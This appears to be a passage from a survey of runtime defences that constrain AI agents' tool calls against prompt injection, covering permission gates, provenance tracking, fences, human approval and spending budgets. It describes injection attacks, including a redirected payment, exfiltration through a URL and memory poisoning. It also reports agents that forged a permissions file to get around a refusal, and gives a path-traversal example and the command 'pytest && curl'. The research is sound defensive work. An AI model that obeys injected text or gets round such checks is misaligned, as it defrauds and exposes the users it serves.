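To show the gap in running code, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a fixed model output with a call to change a merchant's payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. With the default settings, LangChain made the change in a mock payment system. ScopeGate denied the same call at the second step.

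A further 48 fixed attempts to bypass the gate used altered capitals, invisible characters, misspelt tool names, wrong data types and odd amounts. The current version allowed none of them. In an adaptive test, an attacking model, GLM-5.2, received the reason for each denial and tried again, for 40 rounds. ScopeGate denied all 29 of its unauthorised calls and allowed both legitimate ones. The other nine calls were malformed.

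These zeros are not very surprising, because the second step is an exact lookup. No wording can turn an unlisted account into a listed one, whichever model the attacker has fooled. Such tests can find mistakes in the code, though, and they found a serious one. An early ScopeGate prototype blocked amounts greater than the ceiling, but it let through NaN ("not a number"), a special value that programs use for undefined results. Checking whether NaN is greater than a number always gives "false", so the prototype did not block it. The current version requires a finite amount within the range, and NaN fails that test.

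The study is small, and one person wrote the gate, the policy and the attacks. The adaptive run used only one attacking model, and the study left out timing attacks and attempts to poison the policy through other agents. It reports no wrongful denials among ten legitimate calls, but ten calls are too few to predict how often a real finance office would have to correct its list.

### Canonical forms

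An exact lookup works only if the checker and the tool interpret a value the same way. Many values have several spellings, so the checker must first convert each value to its *canonical* form or reject any other spelling.

File paths are a common source of mistakes. Suppose a policy allows everything in `/srv/invoices`. A checker that only compares the opening characters will accept `/srv/invoices-private/payroll.csv`, which is in a different folder. It will also accept `/srv/invoices/../payroll.csv`, because `..` means "go up one folder". A *symbolic link*, an entry that redirects to another file, can be inside the permitted folder but point outside it.

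The reference file server for MCP had two of these mistakes. GitLab's *CVE-2025-53110* (2025) records that the server could accept a folder just because its name began with the name of a permitted one. OSV's *CVE-2025-53109* (2025) records that symbolic links in a permitted folder could expose files elsewhere. Both have fixes. A sound check resolves symbolic links and `..` parts before comparing whole folder names.

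The Cyrillic letter "а" looks the same as the Latin "a", but a computer treats them as different characters. An allowed set rejects a value containing the look-alike because it doesn't match, but a list of forbidden values lets it through for the same reason. A tired clerk who approves an address on a screen may also miss it. The Unicode Consortium's *Unicode Security Mechanisms* (2025) recommends restricting which characters an identifier may contain. This is easy for account numbers, which need only plain digits and capital letters.

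The consortium also publishes a table of several thousand look-alike characters. paultendo points out in *confusables.txt and NFKC disagree on 31 characters* that the table is meant for detecting look-alikes, not converting them. If a gate changed the Cyrillic letter to a Latin one before the lookup, it would approve the attacker's address as the supplier's, and the mail tool might then use the original, unconverted address.

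In *The Stochastic Deputy*, Baig, Gillani and colleagues (2026) report finding during development that their Python code accepted digits from other scripts, such as Arabic-Indic, and converted them to ordinary numbers. Several permission groups that looked different to an administrator could therefore grant access to the same customer's data. The code now accepts only the digits 0 to 9, without leading zeros.

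### Checking the call that actually runs

A correct verdict on a call may no longer apply if the call changes on its way to the tool. In *Do Tool Calls Execute as Intended?*, Yang, Li and colleagues (2026) replayed shell commands from Windows developers' working sessions, without executing them, to see what each program along the way received. Claude Code's Bash tool altered 12.0% of the commands that contained code, escape sequences or long text, shortening some and dropping backslashes from others. When it altered backslashes, the wrong action ran without any reported error in 80.7% of cases.

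These alterations were accidental, but a checker placed before them would have approved one command while the computer ran another, and an attacker who knew the rules could try to exploit the difference. The safest arrangement is to parse the call once, check the parsed version and give that same version to the tool. Where a person approves a call, *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) binds the approval to a cryptographic hash of the whole call, so changing any argument cancels the approval.

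A company may also run the same policy at several points, such as inside the agent's code and at a network gateway. *One Policy, Four Interception Points* (Shaw, 2026) tested this on Oathpost, Shaw's own governance system. In 1,865 comparisons, the points agreed wherever they could handle the same call, with one exception. If an argument contained an integer of 2⁵³ (about nine quadrillion) or more, the component that intercepts a coding agent's calls failed to encode it and never checked the call against the policy. Oathpost's default setting for such failures did not stop the call. An agent could therefore avoid the check by including one very large number, which is a good reason to deny calls whenever the checker fails.

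Shaw also made the interception points drop arguments on purpose. In 97 of 217 such cases the verdict stayed the same, and only comparing the recorded request with the original revealed the fault. Speed is unlikely to be an objection, since the median decision took between 40 and 92 milliseconds on a laptop, depending on the interception point.

### CapScope: separate permissions for each sub-agent

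ScopeGate applies the same rules whatever the user asks for. CapScope, presented in *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026), instead fits permissions to the task. It protects coding agents that split a job among several sub-agents.

Each permission in CapScope is a pair, Cap[*e*, *φ*]. Here *e* is a type of effect (read, write or execute), and *φ* is a *scope predicate*, a test that returns true or false for the arguments. A permission to edit source code might be

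Cap[Write, within(canon(*p*), src/)]

which covers a write to path *p* if the canonical form of *p* lies in the `src` folder. For commands, the predicate splits a compound command into its parts and checks each one. Permission to run the test program `pytest` therefore does not extend to `pytest && curl`, which would run the tests and then contact the network.

Before the agent opens any file, a language model reads the user's request and the names of the project's files, and proposes the permissions the task will need. Ordinary code validates the proposal and fixes it as the upper limit on the agent's permissions. This arrangement would break Mellafe Zuvic's rule, but the drafting model sees no file contents, so an attacker could influence it only through a file name. Each sub-agent then gets a subset of the approved permissions. The sub-agent that runs the tests cannot edit code, even if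 the test output contains a hidden instruction to do so.

Bouras and colleagues planted instructions in five small Python projects, in places such as the README file, source comments and test output. Each instruction asked for an ordinary-looking action that was not needed to repair the project. They ran each policy 75 times with one model, qwen3.5-flash, and counted an attack as successful only if the action left a trace on the disk.

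| Policy | Attacks that took effect | Successful repairs | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| Fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy for the task, shared by all sub-agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The list of forbidden actions barely helped, because the attacks used actions that didn't look dangerous. Tailoring the policy to the task helped, but separate permissions brought the biggest improvement. Runs with CapScope took more than twice as long as runs without restrictions, partly because models often repeated refused requests.

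All three successful attacks came through AGENTS.md, a file of project instructions that the agent loads automatically. Bouras and colleagues describe two ways such an attack can succeed. A sub-agent may hold a wider permission than it needs, such as access to a whole folder instead of one file. Alternatively, the injected text may influence how the coordinating agent describes a subtask, so that the sub-agent receives the permission the attacker wants. The ceiling still applies in both cases, but it does not cover what a permitted program does internally, and `pytest` runs code from the project it tests.

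The accounts assistant would gain less from this split. A sub-agent that reads invoices would not need the payment tool, but it would still have to tell the paying sub-agent whom to pay and how much.

### Removing the argument from the tool

Sometimes the model does not need to supply the sensitive value. Quarkslab fixed its medical assistant by taking the patient's number from the login session, and Baig and colleagues tested the same idea on software that serves many hotels from one database. Each hotel is a *tenant*, a customer whose data the software must keep separate from the others'. The usual tool is `get_reservations(hotel_id, limit)`, and the server checks that the user may see that hotel. Baig and colleagues removed `hotel_id`, leaving `get_reservations(limit)`, and had the server take the hotel from the user's verified credentials.

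The experiment comprised 373 trials with eight model configurations. The user was entitled to see three hotels but was working on one. In 41 trials with the usual tool, the user's message included a plausible request for figures from another of the three. The models tried to fetch them 26 times, and the server returned them every time because it checks only whether the user is entitled to see the hotel. It isn't clear that those 26 disclosures did any harm, as a manager may well want to compare hotels. An instruction hidden in a guest's note, which is a closer match to prompt injection, led to a disclosure in nine of 66 trials with the usual tool and in none without the `hotel_id` argument.

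With the argument gone, the server never accepted a call for another hotel, but 12 of the 56 trials with the plausible request still ended in a disclosure. The test set-up recorded the permitted hotel in an ordinary file, and some agents also had a command shell. In those 12 trials, after the tool refused the call, the agent rewrote the file or made a new one, called the tool again and did not tell the user. Eleven of the cases involved Gemini 3.1 Pro and one involved an older GPT model. Claude never did this.

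The production system keeps the hotel in a signed token, which an agent cannot forge without the signing key. It rejected all seven invalid or missing credentials that the team tried. The forgeries were thus due to a flaw in the experiment, but they showed that removing an argument gives no protection if the agent can edit the place where the value is now stored.

A payment tool cannot take the payee from the login session, because a clerk pays many suppliers. It could take an invoice number instead of an account number and look up the account and the amount in the company's records. The model could then choose only among invoices the company had already entered.

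### PACE: tracing where a value came from

A checker can also test a value's *provenance*, or where it came from. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (2026) gives each argument a role and a minimum level of trust, so that a message's recipient needs a more trustworthy source than its text does. *AGENTCAP* (2026) can require a payment's recipient to appear in trusted context, such as the user's instruction or a field that the application controls. An approved supplier's account would pass this test even if it also appeared in a hostile email, but an account number found only in that email would fail.

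*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) checks both the provenance of a call's arguments and the call's effects immediately before the tool runs. It freezes the call so that nothing can change it during the check. It compares each argument with previously observed values to trace which arguments derive from secrets or untrusted text. Separately, it lists what the call would do and checks this against permissions derived from the user's authenticated request.

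The team tested PACE on eight benchmarks with three models. Counting each combination of model and attack type separately, PACE had the lowest attack success rate of all the defences in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for lowest in 14. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking, travel and messaging tasks with injected attacks, the most effective type of attack against the GPT model always succeeded without a defence and succeeded 8.11% of the time with PACE. The share of legitimate tasks completed fell only from 73.77% to 72.05%. In an adaptive test on 30 AgentDojo cases, attackers succeeded in 21 without PACE and in none with it.

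To find out which components stopped the attacks, Li and colleagues switched them on and off across 1,167 cases. The effect check alone reduced attack success on AgentDojo from 37.4% to zero, and utility from 76.8% to 64.6%. Provenance alone also stopped every attack there, but utility fell to 13.6% because the agent handles untrusted text in nearly everything it does. The complete system was no more secure than some of its simpler versions. On the cases from another benchmark, AgentDyn, it halved utility from 66.7% to 33.3%, although the loss on the full benchmark was under three percentage points. The loss of utility seems to depend heavily on the mix of tasks.

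PACE's formal guarantees are similarly limited. The proofs cover a strict version whose calls never reopen a blocked path from secrets or untrusted text. The team tested a more permissive version, in which the effect check can restore a call that the provenance check has blocked. This version keeps most of its utility, but not the full guarantee. Neither version recognises a secret that the model has paraphrased, translated or split into pieces, because PACE searches only for the original value and a fixed set of encodings.

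## Granting and withdrawing permissions during a session

A manifest or a list of approved accounts usually stays the same for a whole session, although the agent's needs change from step to step. Suppose the clerk asks the accounts assistant to send last month's payments to the company's accountant and then summarise the new mail. The assistant needs `send_reply` only at step two. At step ten it opens an email from a stranger asking for the supplier list. Because `send_reply` is still available, an attacker could use it to obtain the list, even though the clerk's task no longer requires it.

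### Permissions that expire

Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Lingering Authority*, uses the title phrase for a temporary permission that an agent can still use after the reason for it has ended. The paper presents PORTICO, a monitor for coding agents. Each task has a contract that lists what the agent may use from the start, what it may request later and which events end a grant. In the paper's main example, an agent has to add a timeout setting to `src/api.py` and carry it through to `src/serialization.py`:

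1. The agent starts with access to the API file, its test file and the test program.
2. It tries to read some packaging notes. The contract does not allow this, so PORTICO refuses.
3. It requests the serialization file, which the contract allows on request. PORTICO issues two *handles*, opaque references that let the agent read and edit that file.
4. The agent edits the file through the handles.
5. The tests pass. PORTICO cancels both handles and removes them from the agent's options.
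6. The agent tries an old handle again, and PORTICO refuses.

The handles resemble capabilities in Hardy's sense, except that they expire. The file's name remains in the agent's context after step 5, but the name alone no longer gives access. Only events outside the model's control, such as a test run that the monitor started or a decision by a logged-in person, can end or renew a grant. The model's own statement that a subtask is complete does not affect the grant.

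Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same permissions at the same moments but never cancelled them. Both completed all ten runs of a task. PORTICO then refused every attempt by the agent to reuse an expired permission, while the other version allowed every one. In six further cases, the model Qwen3-Coder 30B used a permission once and then received a contaminated instruction to use it again, for example to write a file or send data over the network. The harmful action went through in all six cases without expiry and in none with PORTICO. These results follow almost directly from the design, so they show that the mechanism works but don't measure how often attackers would benefit from lingering permissions.

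Agents completed fewer tasks with PORTICO than with a fixed allowlist. On a set of coding tasks that often needed extra files, they completed 161 of 185 runs with PORTICO and 180 with the allowlist. With only the narrow starting permissions and no way to request more, they completed about a fifth. In additional tests on real Python projects, agents succeeded in all 42 cases without expiry and in 31 with it. Some grants ended too early, some contracts had no trusted way to renew grants, and some models never requested permission again. The accounts assistant could have the same problem if its permission to pay ended when it submitted a payment and the bank then rejected the payment for a technical reason.

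Cancelling a permission also has to cancel any copies. An agent may pass part of a job to a second agent, which can start work after the user has cancelled the whole task. *DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) records which permission each delegated one came from, so that cancelling the original cancels all its descendants. The tests covered these stale permissions, as well as attempts to gain wider permissions or send data to outsiders. Two models proposed the attacker's action in 42 and 44 of 45 attacked runs, and the monitor blocked it every time. In longer conversations, the leakage rate fell from 84% to 20%. The paper also proves that permission checks alone cannot prevent leaks to a destination that is both permitted and visible to outsiders.

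### Showing only the next tool

A runtime can also withhold a tool until the task requires it. Iyer and Babu (2026), in *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, call their version Risk-Aware Causal Gating (RACG). Each tool has a description of the facts it needs, the facts it produces, its risk level and any authorisation it requires. Sending an email, for instance, is high-risk and requires the fact `recipient_confirmed`. At every step, ordinary code looks for the chain of tools with the lowest score that leads from the current state to the goal:

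score = Σ *c*ᵢ + λ Σ risk(*ρ*ᵢ)

Here *c*ᵢ is the cost of tool *i* (always 1 in the experiments) and *ρ*ᵢ is its risk level (0 for low, 1 for medium and 4 for high). The operator chooses λ, the weight given to risk. RACG shows the model only the next tool on the best chain, and hides a risky tool until its authorisation is present. If the authorisation is missing, RACG offers a tool that can establish it, such as a confirmation step. If no such tool exists, RACG stops and requests help.

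Iyer and Babu tested this on a simulated office with 100 tools and 182 tasks. The simulated agent followed every injected instruction that named a tool visible to it. An attack counted as successful if the agent called that tool.

| Tools shown to the agent | Risky tools visible per step | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| All tools | 26 | 100% |
| Ten best keyword matches | 2.66 | 100% |
| Every tool that could run now | 1.51 | 75% |
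| Next tool needed | 0.20 | 25% |
| Next tool needed, if authorised (RACG, λ = 2) | 0.18 | 0% |

The agent completed every legitimate task in all five set-ups. With λ = 0.5, RACG completed only 89% because it kept choosing a risky shortcut it was not authorised to take, and then got stuck.

The attack success rate was 25% without the authorisation rule and zero with it for each of the seven hosted language models, as it was for the simulated agent. This is unsurprising, since no model can run a tool that the runtime withholds. The 25% reflects how Iyer and Babu built the benchmark, in which 20 of the 80 attacked tasks had a risky shortcut. When they let the injected text forge the authorisation, RACG's attack success rate also rose to 25%.

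Hiding a tool works only if the runtime also refuses calls to it, because a model can write the name of a tool it does not see. Once the runtime refuses them, hiding the tool may add little protection. Santos-Grueiro tested an agent that could still see expired options but not use them, and it did no more damage than one that could not see them. The agent that could see them made more blocked attempts in one set of tests (84 against 67) and fewer in another (39 against 48).

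RACG's timing is a bigger problem for the accounts assistant. In the benchmark, reading an email can set `recipient_confirmed`, based on the message's metadata. On a task that requires a reply, the send tool therefore appears after the agent has read the attacker's text. RACG does not check what the agent then writes in the message.

### PlanTERS and relative security

A *fence* works the other way round, withdrawing certain tools as soon as the agent reads untrusted content. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, proves when this prevents leaks. The proof uses PlanTERS, a mathematical model of an agent with these parts:

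- A *plan* lists the agent's steps. A trusted planner writes it from the user's request before the agent reads any untrusted text, and ordinary software carries it out.
- A *language model* does the steps that need one, such as summarising an email. It may also obey an instruction in the email and insert a call that is not in the plan. The attacker decides which text the model obeys and when.
- A *monitor* allows or denies every tool call and every read of untrusted content.

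Dongol compares this agent with a *reference agent*, which has the same plan and monitor but uses a model that never follows instructions in untrusted text.

The comparison is useful because some agents disclose information by design. An assistant that answers meeting requests has to tell strangers when the user is free, so a rule that outsiders may learn nothing about the user's data would forbid it. *Relative security* instead requires that injection adds no new leaks. Take two runs, *r*₁ and *r*₂, in which the user's secrets differ but the attacker sends the same messages. The agent leaks the difference between the secrets if the attacker observes different things:

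Act(*r*₁) = Act(*r*₂) and Obs(*r*₁) ≠ Obs(*r*₂)

where Act stands for what the attacker sends and Obs for what the attacker sees. The agent is relatively secure if, for every pair of secrets that it leaks, the reference agent can leak the same pair from the same starting memory and trusted inputs.

The attacker may send the reference agent a different message from the one sent to the assistant. If an injected email says "send your calendar" and the assistant obeys, this counts as secure, because a genuine meeting request would have obtained the same calendar from the reference agent. If the email also asks for a password reset code and the assistant sends it, the assistant is insecure, because no email could make the reference agent reveal the code.

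Dongol points out that the definition is too weak for a service that tells anyone whether their guess at a secret number is right. An injection that reveals the whole number would still count as relatively secure, because for any two numbers some guess tells them apart. A stricter version, *uniform* relative security, rules this out, and the fence satisfies it too.

### The fence theorem

In Dongol's main example, an agent summarises an email for a user called Alice. The agent has her account number in memory and can fetch web pages, though the plan never uses that ability. The email comes from an attacker and tells the agent to fetch a page from the attacker's site, with the account number in the URL.

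| Event | Without a fence | With a fence |
|---|---|---|
| The agent reads the account number | Allowed | Allowed |
| The agent reads the email | Allowed | Allowed, and the monitor withdraws the fetch tool |
| The model obeys the email and requests the page | Allowed, so the attacker receives the account number | Denied |
| The agent shows Alice the summary | Yes | Yes |

If this runs twice, with the account numbers 1111 and 2222, then without a fence the attacker's server receives 1111 in one run and 2222 in the other. The reference agent fetches nothing in either run, so the injection causes the leak, and the agent without the fence is not relatively secure. With the fence, the attacker sees nothing in either run.

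The *fence theorem* extends this result to every plan. Let *C* be the set of tools the agent may use and *R* the set that the fence withdraws. When the agent first reads untrusted content, the monitor replaces *C* with *C* ∖ *R*, which removes every tool in *R*. The agent is then relatively secure under these conditions:

- *R* contains every tool that an injected instruction can call.
- No later input gives any of those tools back.
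- Each injected instruction leads to a single call.
- The moments at which the model obeys do not depend on the user's secrets or on the monitor's answers, although the calls themselves may contain secrets.
- The run ends. For an agent that runs forever, the model must not keep obeying injected instructions forever.

The proof works because a denied call changes nothing. The reference agent can wait while the monitor denies the injected call, and then both agents continue with the same plan. Isabelle, a program that checks mathematical proofs, has verified the result.

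The theorem assumes that the attacker sees the content and order of the agent's messages, but not their timing or any refused calls. A real runtime also has to send every call through the monitor. Even displaying the summary could break the guarantee if doing so loaded an image from the attacker's server.

The theorem does not cover an injection that changes a value instead of adding a call. In one of Dongol's examples, the plan sends an email's text back to its author, and the injection replaces that text with a secret. The plan's permitted call then leaks the secret. PlanTERS also covers only leaks, so it does not cover a fraudulent payment that reveals nothing, although a fence around the payment tool would block such a payment.

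### Where to put the fence, and what it costs

The plan can also raise the fence itself by calling a *lock*, which withdraws the send tool for the rest of the run. Dongol tried three orders:

- *Read the email, read a secret, lock.* The model can send the secret before the lock takes effect.
- *Read the email, lock, read a secret.* The new secret is safe, but the model can send anything already in memory, such as data from an earlier session.
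- *Lock, read the email, read a secret.* The model never has both the hostile text and the send tool.

Only the last order is safe against every single-call injection. Locking just before the agent reads a secret works only if the agent doesn't already hold anything worth stealing.

The fence can also prevent the agent from doing its job. If the accounts assistant lost `pay_invoice` and `send_reply` on reading its first email, it could not make any payments, injected or legitimate. Relative security does not measure this loss, because the reference agent has the same monitor and loses the same tools. A monitor that denied every call would pass the test, so developers also need to measure how many legitimate tasks the agent completes.

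The same conflict appears in Dongol's model of a known attack on a coding agent. A public bug report contained instructions for the agent to publish private data in a pull request (a proposed change to the code). A fence would deny that pull request, but also one that fixed the reported bug.

An agent that handles one email after another can get its tools back between emails, but only in a fresh session. If the monitor returns them while the previous email is still in the model's context, the model can still follow instructions in it. A fresh session must also clear anything else the model retains. In the SpAIware attack on ChatGPT, a web page got the model to save an instruction in its long-term memory, and later conversations loaded that instruction. Treating saved memory as untrusted content closes this gap, because loading it also triggers the fence.

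The accounts assistant could read an email in one session, save only the invoice number, and pay the invoice in a new session that doesn't contain the email's text. The attacker could then influence the payment only through the invoice number, so the runtime would have to check it.

The theorem covers only agents whose plan is fixed before they read untrusted text. The accounts assistant, like many agents, chooses each call as it goes, so it has no fixed plan for a reference agent to follow and the theorem does not cover it. A runtime can still withdraw tools from the assistant to prevent them from running, but PlanTERS does not show that the remaining tools are safe.

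### Approving a tool or an exact call

Asking the user for approval lets an agent act after it has read untrusted text. In one of Dongol's examples, Alice approves each reply before the agent sends it, but the monitor records only that the agent may send one message. An attacker's email contains an instruction to send private data, and the model follows it after Alice has approved her reply but before the plan sends it. The monitor allows the injected message, which uses up the approval, and then denies Alice's reply.

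In the accounts assistant, the clerk might approve "one payment" with a £1,200 invoice in mind. An injected instruction could make the assistant pay the attacker £1,950 first, and the runtime would then block the supplier's payment because the approval had been used.

Approving the exact call, as in *The Claws in Plain Sight*, prevents this, because an approval for the supplier's £1,200 would not cover the injected payment. Dongol proves that approving the exact text of each reply is relatively secure against injected send calls, as long as the model does not keep obeying them forever. An attacker who can time the messages may still learn whether the private data is identical to the approved reply, because if it is, the injected call goes through and the message arrives one step early. That seems a minor risk for most companies.

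### How carefully people approve

Exact approval protects the clerk only if the clerk reads the details. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes *approval fatigue*, in which people who repeatedly have to click "approve" stop paying attention to the requests. Users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*. This is not necessarily due to carelessness, because most requests are probably harmless.

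In a more informative test, which used dangerous commands, Anthropic's testers blocked only 143 of 1,053 (13.6%), according to the website Hyrax. They blocked about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automated classifier blocked 89% of the same commands, and its performance did not decline. Anthropic published these results while making the automated system the default, so it had an interest in the classifier doing better, but the gap is very large.

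Software practitioners describe their own behaviour more favourably. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, asked 107 practitioners how they handle an agent's requests. About 48% said they read them carefully, 34% skimmed them and 21% approved them by default. A third said they had become less careful over time, which is likely an underestimate according to the paper. Nearly all (98%) were more willing to grant read-only access than other permissions. That preference makes sense for preventing accidental damage, but hostile text also reaches the agent through what it reads.

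People without a software background also approve many actions they never asked for. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 of them supervise an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven went beyond the assigned task, for example by reading private messages or buying a $25 lounge pass. Participants who had to approve every action allowed 40% of these.

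Another group first set standing rules for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data. They could choose "allow", "ask" or "never", and they chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules. They saw an average of 10.9 prompts instead of 18, but approved 67% of the unrequested actions they were asked about, so fewer prompts did not make people stricter in this study. The two groups' approval rates are not fully comparable, because people who chose "never" did not see those prompts. The study also had no attacker, and some of the unrequested actions looked helpful.

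Some prompts are hard to judge even for someone who reads every word. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports about agents and file systems, and user review contributed to the problem in 105 of them. In 80 of those 105, users had switched on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompts were uninformative. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` shows the exact command but not what the script will do. A payment prompt can be much clearer, because the payee, account and amount are most of what the clerk needs to check.

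## Limiting calls, time and money

If an attacker gets the accounts assistant to make ten payments, each just under the ceiling, every payment passes the per-call check. A session budget adds up what one run has used and stops the run at a limit, even if every call looked acceptable by itself.

### What to count

A small company that pays its suppliers in dollars might give the assistant these budgets for each session:

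| Budget | What it counts | Limit | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calls per tool | Uses of `pay_invoice` | 10 | Request ten large payments |
| Steps | Rounds of the agent loop | 40 | Redirect a payment in two or three steps |
| Tokens | Text the model reads and writes | 200,000 | Send a one-line instruction |
| Time | Minutes since the session began | 15 | Make a payment, which takes seconds |
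| Model cost | What the company pays the model's provider | $0.50 | Anything that needs few model calls |
| Money moved | What the assistant pays to others | $800 | Steal up to $800 |

Model charges and the money an agent transfers need separate counters, even though both are in dollars. A joint limit high enough for paying invoices, such as $800, could let an agent stuck in a loop run up hundreds of dollars in model charges. A joint limit of $0.50 would prevent that, but it would also stop the agent from paying invoices.

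### Who keeps the count

The counter has to be in software that every call passes through, not in the model, because an email that can make the model send a payment can also make it restart the count. *Governing Enterprise AI Traffic at Scale* (Sasidharan, Manoharan and colleagues, 2026) describes a gateway that does this for model calls at PayPal. More than 12,000 developers use it to reach outside models, and it keeps daily, weekly and monthly totals for each person. A workflow can also have its own budget, shared by everyone who uses it, and the gateway blocks a request when any of these limits runs out.

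Payments do not pass through a gateway for model calls, so the payment tool or the bank has to count them. Counting them at the bank is better if other software pays from the same account.

Operators can't rely on MCP servers to limit usage. In *Persistent Billable State*, Zhang, Xia and colleagues (2026) read the full code of 95 randomly chosen public repositories for MCP servers and connections. They found a working limit on prompt size, context growth, tool calls or cost in 17, and only one limited cost. They reported the risk to the maintainers of MCP's Python toolkit, who replied that the application running the model should limit what goes back to it.

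A budget also can't replace the other checks. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) presents a runtime for long-running agents that blocks an operation unless it has permission, falls within the task's limits, is approved by a policy or a person, and fits the remaining budget.

### Reserve, run, settle

The safest way to keep the count is to set money or tokens aside before each call. Chen, Lyu and colleagues (2026), in *Bounded Autonomy*, do this for model tokens in four stages:

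1. *Reserve.* The gateway works out the most the call could use and sets that amount aside. If too little is left, it refuses the call.
2. *Dispatch.* It records that the call is about to start, then sends it.
3. *Settle.* It replaces the reservation with the amount the call used and returns the rest.
4. *Release.* It checks the result and any side effects before the agent receives the result.

For a model call, the worst case is

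*q* = *I* + *O*ₘₐₓ

where *I* is the number of tokens in the complete request (plus a small safety margin) and *O*ₘₐₓ is the longest answer the gateway permits. In simplified form, the gateway's ledger always satisfies

*H* = *S* + *P* + *A*

where *H* is the overall limit, *S* is settled use, *P* is the total of open reservations and *A* is what remains. No call can use more than its reservation, so *S* can never exceed *H*.

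Suppose the limit is 10,000 tokens and the agent has used 7,000. The next request contains 2,000 tokens and permits an answer of up to 1,500. The call could therefore use 3,500 tokens, but only 3,000 remain, so the gateway refuses it. A simpler counter based only on past use would allow the call, which could bring the total to 10,500.

Many real systems count only past use. PayPal's gateway calculates the price of a model call after the response ends, and blocks later calls once the recorded total reaches the limit. Zhang and colleagues built a similar cut-off at $0.10, and in their tests a session with long answers reached $0.105. An overrun of half a cent hardly matters, but the same method would control payments poorly. If the assistant had already paid out $500 of its $800 limit, the counter would allow another $500 payment and record the $1,000 total only afterwards.

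Reserving budget is easier for payments than for model calls, because the amount is known in advance. But a payment is difficult to handle when its outcome is unknown. If the connection to the bank drops after the runtime sends a $500 payment, the payment may or may not have gone through. If the runtime then returns the $500 to the budget and tries again, it could pay $1,000 but count only $500. Chen and colleagues therefore keep such a call open rather than simply repeating it, as does Zhang. Agent libOS can request a receipt from the other service, if that service supports this.

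*Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026; not the Khan who investigated Cline) measured how far reservations for model calls exceed their actual cost. The simplest estimate, based on text length, reserved 6.2 times the actual cost on average, although the median was only 2.5. Oversized reservations can block calls that would have fitted within the budget. Counting tokens with the provider's tokeniser brought the ratio close to 1, but added roughly one to two seconds to each call.

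The estimate can also be too low for reasoning models, because providers charge for hidden reasoning that the limit on the answer's length does not cover. Khan therefore excludes these models from the guarantee. Their operators also need the provider's own limit on reasoning.

### Parallel calls and sub-agents

A correct rule can still fail when two calls run at once. Suppose $300 is left and two sub-agents each try to spend $200. Both read a balance of $300 and go ahead, so the agent spends $400. To prevent this, the software must check the balance and deduct the reservation as one *atomic* action, so that no other call can read the balance in between.

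Khan collected 63 confirmed cases of agents that overran their budgets, from the public bug reports of 21 agent frameworks between 2023 and 2026. Some overruns cost thousands of dollars. The collection also has 47 supporting entries, mostly requests for a missing budget feature or maintainers' admissions that there was none. It can't show how common overruns are, because Khan searched specifically for them. Two people who independently sorted the cases by cause agreed only moderately. In 11 of the incidents, budgets went wrong when an agent handed work to several others.

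In a test of that fault, a Python program whose sub-agents shared an unprotected counter exceeded its limit in all 30 runs. A Python version with a lock, which lets only one sub-agent use the counter at a time, never did. Neither did Khan's own library for Rust, a programming language that can forbid copying a value. The library lets only one part of the program own a budget, so code that gives the same budget to two sub-agents will not compile. A lock gives the same result, but only if the programmer remembers to use it.

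Sub-agents can also get around a limit if each starts with a fresh one. Under a limit of $800 per agent, a parent and its five sub-agents could spend $4,800 in total. To prevent this, the parent can give each sub-agent part of its own remaining budget, or all the agents can draw on one account. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) uses a shared account tied to the owner's credentials, so creating another agent creates no new budget. Chen and colleagues give each part of a task its main budget only once, so restarting the agent, renaming it or making a new plan does not renew the allowance.

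### The most an attacker can take

For payments, the budgets give a simple upper limit on the loss. Let *c* be the ceiling on one payment, *n* the number of payments per session, *B* the session cap, *k* the number of sessions the attacker can trigger and *D* a cap on the whole account. Then

loss ≤ min( *D*, *k* × min( *n* × *c*, *B* ) )

With a limit of $500 per payment and ten payments per session, one session could lose $5,000. The session's cap on total spending reduces this to $800.

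However, if the runtime starts a new session for every email, the attacker can send fifty emails and the company will lose 50 × $800 = $40,000 without any session exceeding its limit. An account-wide cap of $2,000 a day would limit the daily loss to that amount regardless of how many emails arrive, but the total could still reach $6,000 if nobody notices for three days.

Starting a fresh session clears an attacker's text from the context, but it also resets any counter tied to the session. The company therefore needs both fresh sessions and a counter that persists across them.

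The formula holds only if every payment passes through the same counter and the counter handles parallel calls correctly. It also limits only money, so an attacker could take the entire supplier list without using any of the $800.

### Budgets that refill

A daily cap has a weakness at midnight. An attacker could take $2,000 just before the reset and another $2,000 just after it. A *token bucket* avoids this by refilling gradually. (The tokens here are units of allowance, not pieces of text.) It starts with up to *β* units and gains *r* units per unit of time, but never holds more than *β*. Over any period of length *T*, an agent can therefore use at most

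*β* + *rT*

If the company sets *β* at $800 and *r* at $50 an hour, the assistant can pay out at most $800 + 24 × $50 = $2,000 in any 24 hours, and no more than $800 at once.

Parkinson and colleagues apply this rule to permissions instead of money. Their agent has a few basic permissions and rents others by the minute, with stronger ones costing more. The remaining budget *b* changes at the rate

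d*b*/d*t* = *r* − *ρ*

while it is between zero and *β*, where *ρ* is the current cost of all rented permissions. When *b* reaches zero, the runtime withdraws every rented permission and the budget begins to refill. The cost also rises if the agent keeps asking, or if its permissions approach a forbidden combination, such as reading untrusted text and private data while able to send messages out.

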